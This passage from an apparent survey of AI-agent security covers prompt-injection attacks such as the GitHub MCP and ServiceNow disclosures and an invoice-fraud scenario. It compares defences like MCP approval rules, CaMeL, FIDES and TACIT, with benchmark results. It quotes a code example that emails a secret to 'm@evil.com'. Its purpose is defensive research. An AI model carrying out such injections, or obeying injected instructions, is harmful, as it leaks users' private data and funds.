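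The storage service can't distinguish Alice's application from the attacker's client, because both requests carry Alice's cookie and the proxy's identity. The proxy can, so MCP requires it to keep a list of the clients each user has approved. Before contacting the storage service for a new client, the proxy must ask Alice to approve that client and show her its name, the permissions it requests and the address that will receive the reply. Like Amazon's external IDs, this makes the check include the party behind the deputy, and it works because each approval applies to only one client. MCP has deprecated the automatic registration that step 2 relies on, but proxies that still support it remain exposed.

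MCP also relies on identity rather than possession for the references that servers issue. For example, a server may create a reference for a shopping cart and expect the agent to send it back with later requests. MCP forbids servers to treat possession of the reference as proof of identity, and recommends storing each cart under both the user's ID and the reference. A server that does this refuses Bob if he guesses the reference to Alice's cart. With Close's web-keys, by contrast, anyone who has the address may use it.

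These rules stop deputies that mix up clients, users or services. Alice's agent doesn't mix up any of them in either form of the invoice attack, so it can follow every rule and still do what Bob wants.

The rules on permissions may even help Bob. When a client lacks a permission, the server should identify the permissions the operation requires. A client acting for a user should then request a new token that combines those permissions with the ones it already requested, so its access tends to grow during a job. If the agent has no access to Alice's files when it reads Bob's text, its client may request it. The attack's success could then depend on whether Alice approves the request on a consent screen.

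### Two disclosures from 2025

Security researchers have shown attacks like form A on real products. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes one against agents connected to GitHub, where programmers store code in public and private repositories. Anyone can report a problem in a public repository, so the researchers put instructions for the agent in a report. The repository's owner then asked the agent, which ran on Claude 4 Opus, to look at the open reports. The agent read the owner's private repositories and published details from them in the public one, including the owner's salary and plans to move abroad.

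GitHub allowed the agent's requests because the agent was using the owner's account, which has permission to read the private repositories and write to the public one. Invariant Labs found no flaw in the GitHub MCP server's code and concluded that GitHub couldn't fix the problem alone.

A credential limited to the public repository would have prevented the leak, and Invariant Labs recommends limiting agents to the repositories they need. But it considers token permissions too rigid for many agents, and suggests a rule that an agent may use only one repository per session. An ordinary access list can't express this rule because it depends on what the agent has already done. The rule would also block legitimate work that involves two repositories.

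The other attack targeted ServiceNow, whose software many companies use to handle support tickets. AppOmni, a security company, created a user who could file tickets but not read other people's. This user filed a ticket containing hidden instructions. When an administrator asked an agent to process it, the agent called a second agent that could read and edit records. Together they copied the contents of a restricted ticket into the user's own ticket, where the user could read them.

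ServiceNow's access lists had correctly kept the user from opening the restricted ticket directly, but its agents run by default with the permissions of the person who started the conversation, in this case the administrator. Bob used the same weakness of impersonation when he hid an instruction in source code for Alice to compile. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, AppOmni got an agent to give an attacker's account the administrator role.

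ServiceNow knew who had written the malicious ticket. If the system had limited the agent to what both the administrator and the ticket's author could read, the copying would have failed. But the agent also couldn't have looked up similar tickets from other people while processing this one, which is a likely reason to use an agent. AppOmni recommends having a person approve each use of a powerful tool and separating agents that read outside text from agents that can change records.

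Researchers staged both attacks, so neither shows how often criminals do this, and both of their companies sell products for monitoring agents. Still, Invariant Labs published the public repository it had used and a record of the agent's actions. ServiceNow said that its system works as intended and updated its documentation to explain the risk, according to The Hacker News' *ServiceNow AI Agents Can Be Tricked* (2025).

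### What identity checks do for agents

Identity-based checks work much better when the person giving the instructions is the one who lacks permission. Siu and colleagues give the example of an employee who asks a company's agent for everyone's salary. The agent can read the personnel database because it does administrative work there, but the employee can't.

In a version of Hardy's attack with an agent in place of the compiler, an employee asks the agent for data the employee isn't allowed to read. The attack works if the agent queries the database with its own account. If the agent instead presents a token for the employee, the database refuses the request, however the employee words it. This protection is valuable for any agent that serves a whole company, but it requires that the agent have no account of its own that can access the same data.

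With separate identities, a bank could also let Alice pay anyone but let her agent pay only accounts she has paid before. This would stop form B for an established supplier, and the bank already has the list of those accounts. A bank that can't tell Alice from her agent can't apply the rule without restricting her too.

South argues for separate identities mainly because services often log an agent's action exactly as they would log the user's own, so an investigator can't tell who did it. A token that names both fixes this. In form A, it would let Alice show that her agent had sent the file. *Delegation Without Trust* goes further and requires cryptographic evidence connecting every step to a person's grant of authority. In form B, that evidence would be complete and valid, because Alice did authorize her agent to pay the invoice. It would help her reconstruct the payment but wouldn't have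 stopped it.

An agent with its own identity is also easier to shut off. If Alice's agent uses her session, she may have to log out everywhere or change her password to stop it. An administrator can disable an agent that has its own identity without affecting Alice's access. South wants this to work across every connected service, using SCIM, a standard that companies already use to create and remove employees' accounts. South's version deletes the agent's identity permanently, while *Authorization Architectures* recommends marking the agent as retired so that its records remain available for later investigations.

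Administrators have more reasons to revoke an agent's access than an employee's. *Authorization Architectures* lists the end of a task, a change of model or prompt, and signs of an injection among them. A token that expires after an hour doesn't cover these cases, because an agent that finishes its task in five minutes can still use the token for another 55.

South thinks that existing standards work well when one organisation controls both the agent and its tools and the user is present. They work less well when an agent crosses between organisations, runs for days, or starts other agents. South also expects that asking users to approve more actions won't scale, because people will face thousands of requests and approve them by reflex.

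Standards bodies have only begun to fill these gaps. *AI Identity* reports that both the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) and industry guidelines cite the lack of a standard format for delegation chains as an obstacle to adoption by companies. In February 2026, a draft NIST concept paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), proposed a project to address agent identity. According to Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents*, the project would adapt existing identity systems to agents, and the paper asks companies and agencies how they identify and control them. The draft received more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), which announces a 10 November conference talk by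 one of the draft's authors.

Agents that work for several people at once are a harder case. A team may share one agent in a chat channel, even though Alice is allowed to see the salary file and Bob isn't. South knows of no popular protocol that supports sharing an agent this way. The whitepaper recommends matching an agent's permissions to those of the people who will receive its output, which would keep the agent from opening the salary file in that channel. But if the agent read the file an hour earlier in a private conversation with Alice and still remembers it, it can tell Bob what the file contains without making a request that a service could check.

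## Agents limited by capabilities and data labels

The software that runs Alice's agent could still keep her salary from Bob if it recorded who may see each piece of information. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) does this by attaching a label to every value. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan another, only Bob and Carol may read text made from both. A message containing Alice's salary would be labeled as readable only by Alice, so the software would refuse to post it where Bob can read it.

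Other designers start from capabilities and give the agent references only to the resources a task needs. Both approaches add a check in the agent's own software, often called its harness, which has more information than the bank or the file service about why the agent is making a request.

### How CaMeL handles the invoice

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, short for "Capabilities for Machine Learning", is a prominent example. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It builds on Simon Willison's idea of using two models, one that plans and never reads outside text, and one that reads outside text and has no tools. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe a design that would handle Alice's request in five steps:

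1. The planning model receives Alice's request and writes a plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. It has not read the invoice.
2. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It stores what they return in variables, which the planning model doesn't see.
3. When the program needs a fact from the invoice, the interpreter gives the text to the reading model, which returns the fact in a fixed format.
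4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it. CaMeL's designers call these labels capabilities.
5. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function examines the tool, its arguments and their labels, and allows or denies the call.

The plan might look like this:

```
invoice = read_email(sender="printing firm")
bill    = parse_with_ai("amount and account number", invoice)
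send_money(to=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
send_email(to="printing firm", body="Paid")
```

In form A, Bob's text asks for the salary file. The attack fails because nothing in the program opens that file or attaches anything to the reply, and Bob's text arrives after the program has been written. In form B, Bob only needs to change the value of `bill`. The reading model copies his account number, and the program pays him unless a policy blocks the payment. Nikolaou and colleagues give an example of such a policy, which denies a payment if the recipient or the amount came from an untrusted source.

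That policy also denies the legitimate payment, because the firm's real account number arrives by email too. But CaMeL, unlike IFEDAC, labels each value separately, so the program can read the invoice and take the account number from Alice's records. A policy that restricts only the recipient will then allow the payment. For a new supplier, Alice has to confirm the number herself.

CaMeL's capabilities are labels that record a value's history for a policy to check. They are not object capabilities, because holding one doesn't grant permission to use anything. The interpreter calls tools with whatever access the harness has. Each label's list of readers works like an access control list that travels with the data. CaMeL's results are therefore mostly evidence about provenance tracking.

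The tracking also has gaps. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, adapt a classic example, which amounts to this:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when the program assigns to it in a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, the fourth line never assigns to `rich`, so `rich` keeps its public label. The email then goes out, even though the value of `rich` reveals the balance.

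### What the protection costs

AgentDojo, a benchmark for such defences, has 97 ordinary tasks in banking, travel, office work and the messaging program Slack. It hides an attacker's instructions in the data the agent reads, then records whether the agent completed the user's task and whether the attacker got what they wanted. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) reproduces CaMeL's published results for 963 pairs of a task and an attack. With OpenAI's o4-mini, CaMeL completed the user's task in about 76% of the pairs, and one attack succeeded. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, no attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 1.4% of the travel tasks.

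Policy checks account for much of the drop in completed tasks. When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks, it completed 37.5% of them with policy checks, about half as many as without them. The checks stopped every attack, but only a few attacks succeeded without them. In 97 of the 144 banking pairs, the attack needed a tool that the plan for the user's task would normally never call, as in form A, so fixing the plan in advance was nearly always enough to stop it. The other 47 pairs resemble form B, because the plan already contained what the attacker needed. With one model and no policy checks, CaMeL resisted 138 of 141 attempts on those pairs.

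Planning in advance lowers success rates less for newer models. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested five models on tasks in which one agent directs four specialists in managing industrial equipment. CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The researchers ran CaMeL without policies, so these figures exclude the effect of policies that Garby and colleagues measured. Most failures occurred because the model committed to a plan before seeing the data that showed another step was needed.

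Peters-Gill and colleagues also found that labels can be lost when one agent passes text to another. If an agent includes outside text in its instructions to a second agent, the second agent's planning model treats that text as a request from its user. In their demonstration, text hidden in a database led a notification agent to email job applicants' details to an outside address, even though every agent ran CaMeL. Their fix sends outside data separately from instructions, with its labels attached. Across 949 attacks per model, the average success rate was 12.9% with no defence, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0% with the fix.

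### Labels and object capabilities compared

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the model choose each step as it goes. Once a simple agent of this kind with labels reads one untrusted email, its whole conversation counts as untrusted and it may no longer make payments. With GPT-4o, such checks reduced the share of banking tasks the simple agent completed from 98.8% to 37.5%. FIDES stores untrusted results in variables and shows the model only their names. To get a fact from a variable, the model can query a second model that has no tools. The harness can restrict that answer to yes or no, which leaves an attacker little room for instructions, though Costa and colleagues didn't include this restriction in their test. FIDES completed 52.5% of banking tasks with its checks on.

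An agent completes more tasks under a rule about each tool-call argument than under a rule about the whole conversation. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares the two on AgentDojo, also with GPT-4o. Under the FIDES rule, which forbids consequential actions after the agent has read untrusted content, the agent completed 33.2% of its tasks. Under a rule about where each argument came from, it completed 62.5%. With only the benchmark's built-in defence, it completed 83.7%.

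Odersky and colleagues' system, TACIT, uses object capabilities. The agent writes programs in Scala, and the compiler rejects any program that uses a resource without holding a capability for it. Secret data arrives in a wrapper that accepts only functions without side effects, so a program can summarize a secret document but can't email it. A separate trusted model processes the contents, and the agent's model never sees them.

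Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of secrets and made 131 attempts per model to extract them. No secrets leaked with the wrapper on. With it off, Claude Sonnet 4.6 revealed secrets in response to 2 of 11 direct or deceptive requests, and MiniMax M2.5 in response to 8 of 11. Writing programs instead of calling tools barely affected ordinary work. Three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 points higher on simulated customer service, and the one model tested on software repairs did slightly worse.

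The table shows the share of tasks that each system completed while under attack on AgentDojo.

| System and model | Banking | Office | Slack | Travel | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence, GPT-4o | 84.0% | 62.8% | 67.6% | 73.5% | 152 |
| FIDES, GPT-4o | 56.9% | 64.0% | 41.9% | 37.9% | 0 |
| CaMeL, o4-mini | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| TACIT, o4-mini | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
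| CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |

The first two rows exclude attacks that Costa and colleagues thought the benchmark had misjudged. TACIT's one failure may also have been misjudged, because the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel.

In TACIT's banking interface, text from files arrives in the wrapper, and the payment function accepts only ordinary text. A program therefore can't pay an account number that it found in a file. This would block form B if the invoice were a file, but it would also block the legitimate payment until Alice typed the number herself.

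### Names in text

Capabilities protect the compiler because Alice gives it a reference instead of a file name. An agent mostly receives text, such as "the printing firm's invoice" from Alice or a file name from Bob, which the harness has to turn into something a service accepts. If the harness looks up every name with the agent's own access, f(agent, read, salary file) returns "yes" no matter who wrote the name, which recreates Hardy's problem. A web-key would avoid this, but a file name in an email carries no permission.

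TACIT's `requestFileSystem` function has this weakness. It takes a directory name as text and gives the program a capability for everything in that directory. If a note from Bob leads the agent to request the directory containing Alice's salary file, the compiler keeps the program within that directory but doesn't track that Bob suggested it. The wrapper still protects the file if somebody has marked that directory as secret. Odersky and colleagues describe a stricter arrangement for summarizing contracts, in which the harness gives the agent one document collection and one output file. The program can't open anything else, whatever name Bob writes.

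Alternatively, the harness could look up each name with the permissions of whoever supplied it, using Alice's for names in her request and Bob's for names in his email. This is Tymshare's hat switching, with a label on each name to show which hat to use. CaMeL could supply these labels because its interpreter keeps values from the email apart from the plan. An ordinary agent reads the request and the email as one stream of text. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes how labels can then spread until every piece of data has all of them, making the labels useless.

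A list of approved names doesn't solve the problem either. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) reports a test of Progent, which enforces rules about the tools and values an agent may use, including a list of approved email addresses. In some tasks the user wants to email a colleague named Lily, while in others an attacker wants the agent to email her. If the list includes her address, the attack succeeds, and if it doesn't, the legitimate tasks fail. Progent blocked 97.7% of attacks in this test but allowed only 69.2% of legitimate runs.

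*Agent-Sentry*'s own system checks where the address came from and, in unclear cases, uses another model to judge whether the action fits the user's request. It allowed 96.4% of legitimate runs and blocked 96.8% of attacks. The same version allowed only 64.4% of legitimate runs on the original AgentDojo tasks and those of a related benchmark, which were not used to build its rules. This was partly because users in those tasks often leave the details to a document.

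FIDES can restrict the model to the names of existing variables, so Bob's text can't introduce a new resource, but the model might still choose the wrong variable. *Beyond Proof of Possession* (2026) notes that capabilities solve the classical case of one request, but that a program working through many steps may hold several unrelated authorities at once. An agent with one capability for paying the printing firm and another for paying Alice's rent still has to use the right one.

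### Turning a request into grants

The developer of an ordinary program can decide once which permissions it needs for a task such as "pay the printing firm's invoice". *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) notes that a general-purpose agent has no developer to make that decision for each task, only a user who describes the task and may know nothing about security. Agents don't reliably limit their own access either. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a test with 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents chose a more powerful tool than they needed over 30% of the time.

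Some systems therefore have a model write the permissions before the agent reads anything from outside. *ToolFence* (2026) gives this model only the user's authenticated request and descriptions of the tools. The request must contain explicit evidence for any permission to change something. *ClawGuard* (2026) has a model list the websites, files and tools that the task needs, and sends doubtful actions to the user for approval.

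The result can be a real capability. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) defines a capability as a signed token that names a tool, the values it may receive, the type of operation and an expiry time. If Alice's agent held one such token for a payment to the firm's account as listed in her records and another for a single reply, it would resist both forms of the attack, as it would with a request-scoped token.

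Mellafe Zuvic rejects letting a model grant permissions, because an injection that corrupts the agent's action could also corrupt its permissions. That objection is strong against an agent that widens its own permissions during a job, but weaker against *ToolFence*, where the model finishes writing the permissions before Bob's text arrives. However, if Alice pastes Bob's email into her request, his words become part of the authenticated text.

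A model can also misjudge an honest request. If Alice asks the agent to pay the invoice, she may or may not want it to check the price against her contract. A grant that is too narrow would make the agent fail, and one that is too broad would give Bob more permissions to exploit. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* describes PAuth, which derives permissions from parts of the user's request, and warns that it can be ambiguous how to divide the request. The paper recommends that tests of such systems count wrongful refusals and the burden on users as well as the attacks prevented.

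When a grant depends on Alice's approval, the harness can check in advance that the agent will ask her for it. Nikolaou and colleagues' system translates a CaMeL plan into a model of every path the plan could take and checks those paths against rules before any tool runs. If the rule is that Alice must approve every new payee, the system rejects a plan with a path that skips this step and reports that path to the planning model.

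Even a well-chosen grant can allow a leak. Suppose Alice also wants the agent to answer the firm's question about an old order, so she grants it access to her order records. Bob reads the firm's mailbox, so he will see whatever the agent puts in its reply. *DelegateGuard* (2026) proves that a capability check which ignores the content and quantity of data cannot prevent leaks to a destination that the agent may write to and an outsider can observe. Labels could help if each of Alice's order records listed who may read it and some of those lists excluded the firm.

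### When the user says to follow a document

Some tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a document. In one of AgentDojo's banking tasks, for example, the agent must read a file and make a payment according to its instructions. FIDES blocks many such tasks, which Costa and colleagues consider the intended result because reading the file makes the agent's context untrusted. They classify about 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks as data-dependent, meaning that the right steps depend on what the agent finds.

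Garby and colleagues let the planning model endorse untrusted data, which allows the data to affect a payment. The model has to include the endorsement in its plan before it reads the data, so a reviewer can find it there. Their agent completed roughly twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on. Two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with another payment request.

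No label can distinguish these attacks from honest use, because in both cases the user told the agent to obey the file and the file came from the same place. The system refuses both unless there is endorsement. Once there is, only a judgement about the content, such as a warning that the payee is new, could show that something is wrong. CaMeL is not designed to prevent this case.

Such requests can also undo CaMeL's separation of planning from reading. One task asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model, which had no access to the file's contents, wrote a program with a branch for every tool and made the choice of branch depend on those contents. With the policies off, the attacker's text could then trigger any tool, even though the planning model never received that text.

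### Usability, coverage and existing services

Defenders of identity-based checks can point out that logins and tokens don't make agents fail half their tasks. Systems unrelated to CaMeL have the same loss. Garby and colleagues report that TypeGuard, the system from *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on. Its designers think many of those tasks involve data flows that no secure policy would allow, and suggest asking the user to confirm them, which returns part of the work to Alice. But an identity-based check avoids the refusals only by letting the questionable flows through.

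The newest models also resist many attacks on their own. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, none of the 949 attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 with no defence, and 1.5% succeeded against Claude Fable 5. If that held everywhere, few people would accept CaMeL's drawbacks. But Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that stronger attacks that adapt to the model may do better, and *Language-Based Agent Control* notes that OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. A good model lowers the chance that Bob's text works, but *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (2026) argues that attackers can raise it again, though they can't make an agent misuse a tool it doesn't have.

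Coverage is harder for designs that plan in advance. An agent that operates a screen has to plan for windows and error messages it hasn't seen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports that plans for such work averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 on AgentDojo. Each added branch is another point where outside text can influence which steps the program takes, even if the text can't add new ones.

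Adoption is also difficult because existing services generally recognise accounts and broad tokens rather than a capability for one invoice. TACIT can work in front of these services without changes to the agent, which connects to it through the Model Context Protocol. Its shared code is about 1,000 lines, and each customer service domain needed a few hundred more. But TACIT controls only what passes through it. Its guarantees don't cover programs that the agent starts outside Scala, so an administrator has to restrict those with a list of permitted commands or a sandbox.

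*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) advises developers to tie permissions to the current task rather than to a lasting agent identity. If the bank offers only a token for Alice's whole account, the harness must hold the token and enforce the narrower limit itself. If the agent can also use a browser where Alice is logged in to the bank, it can access her account without going through the harness.
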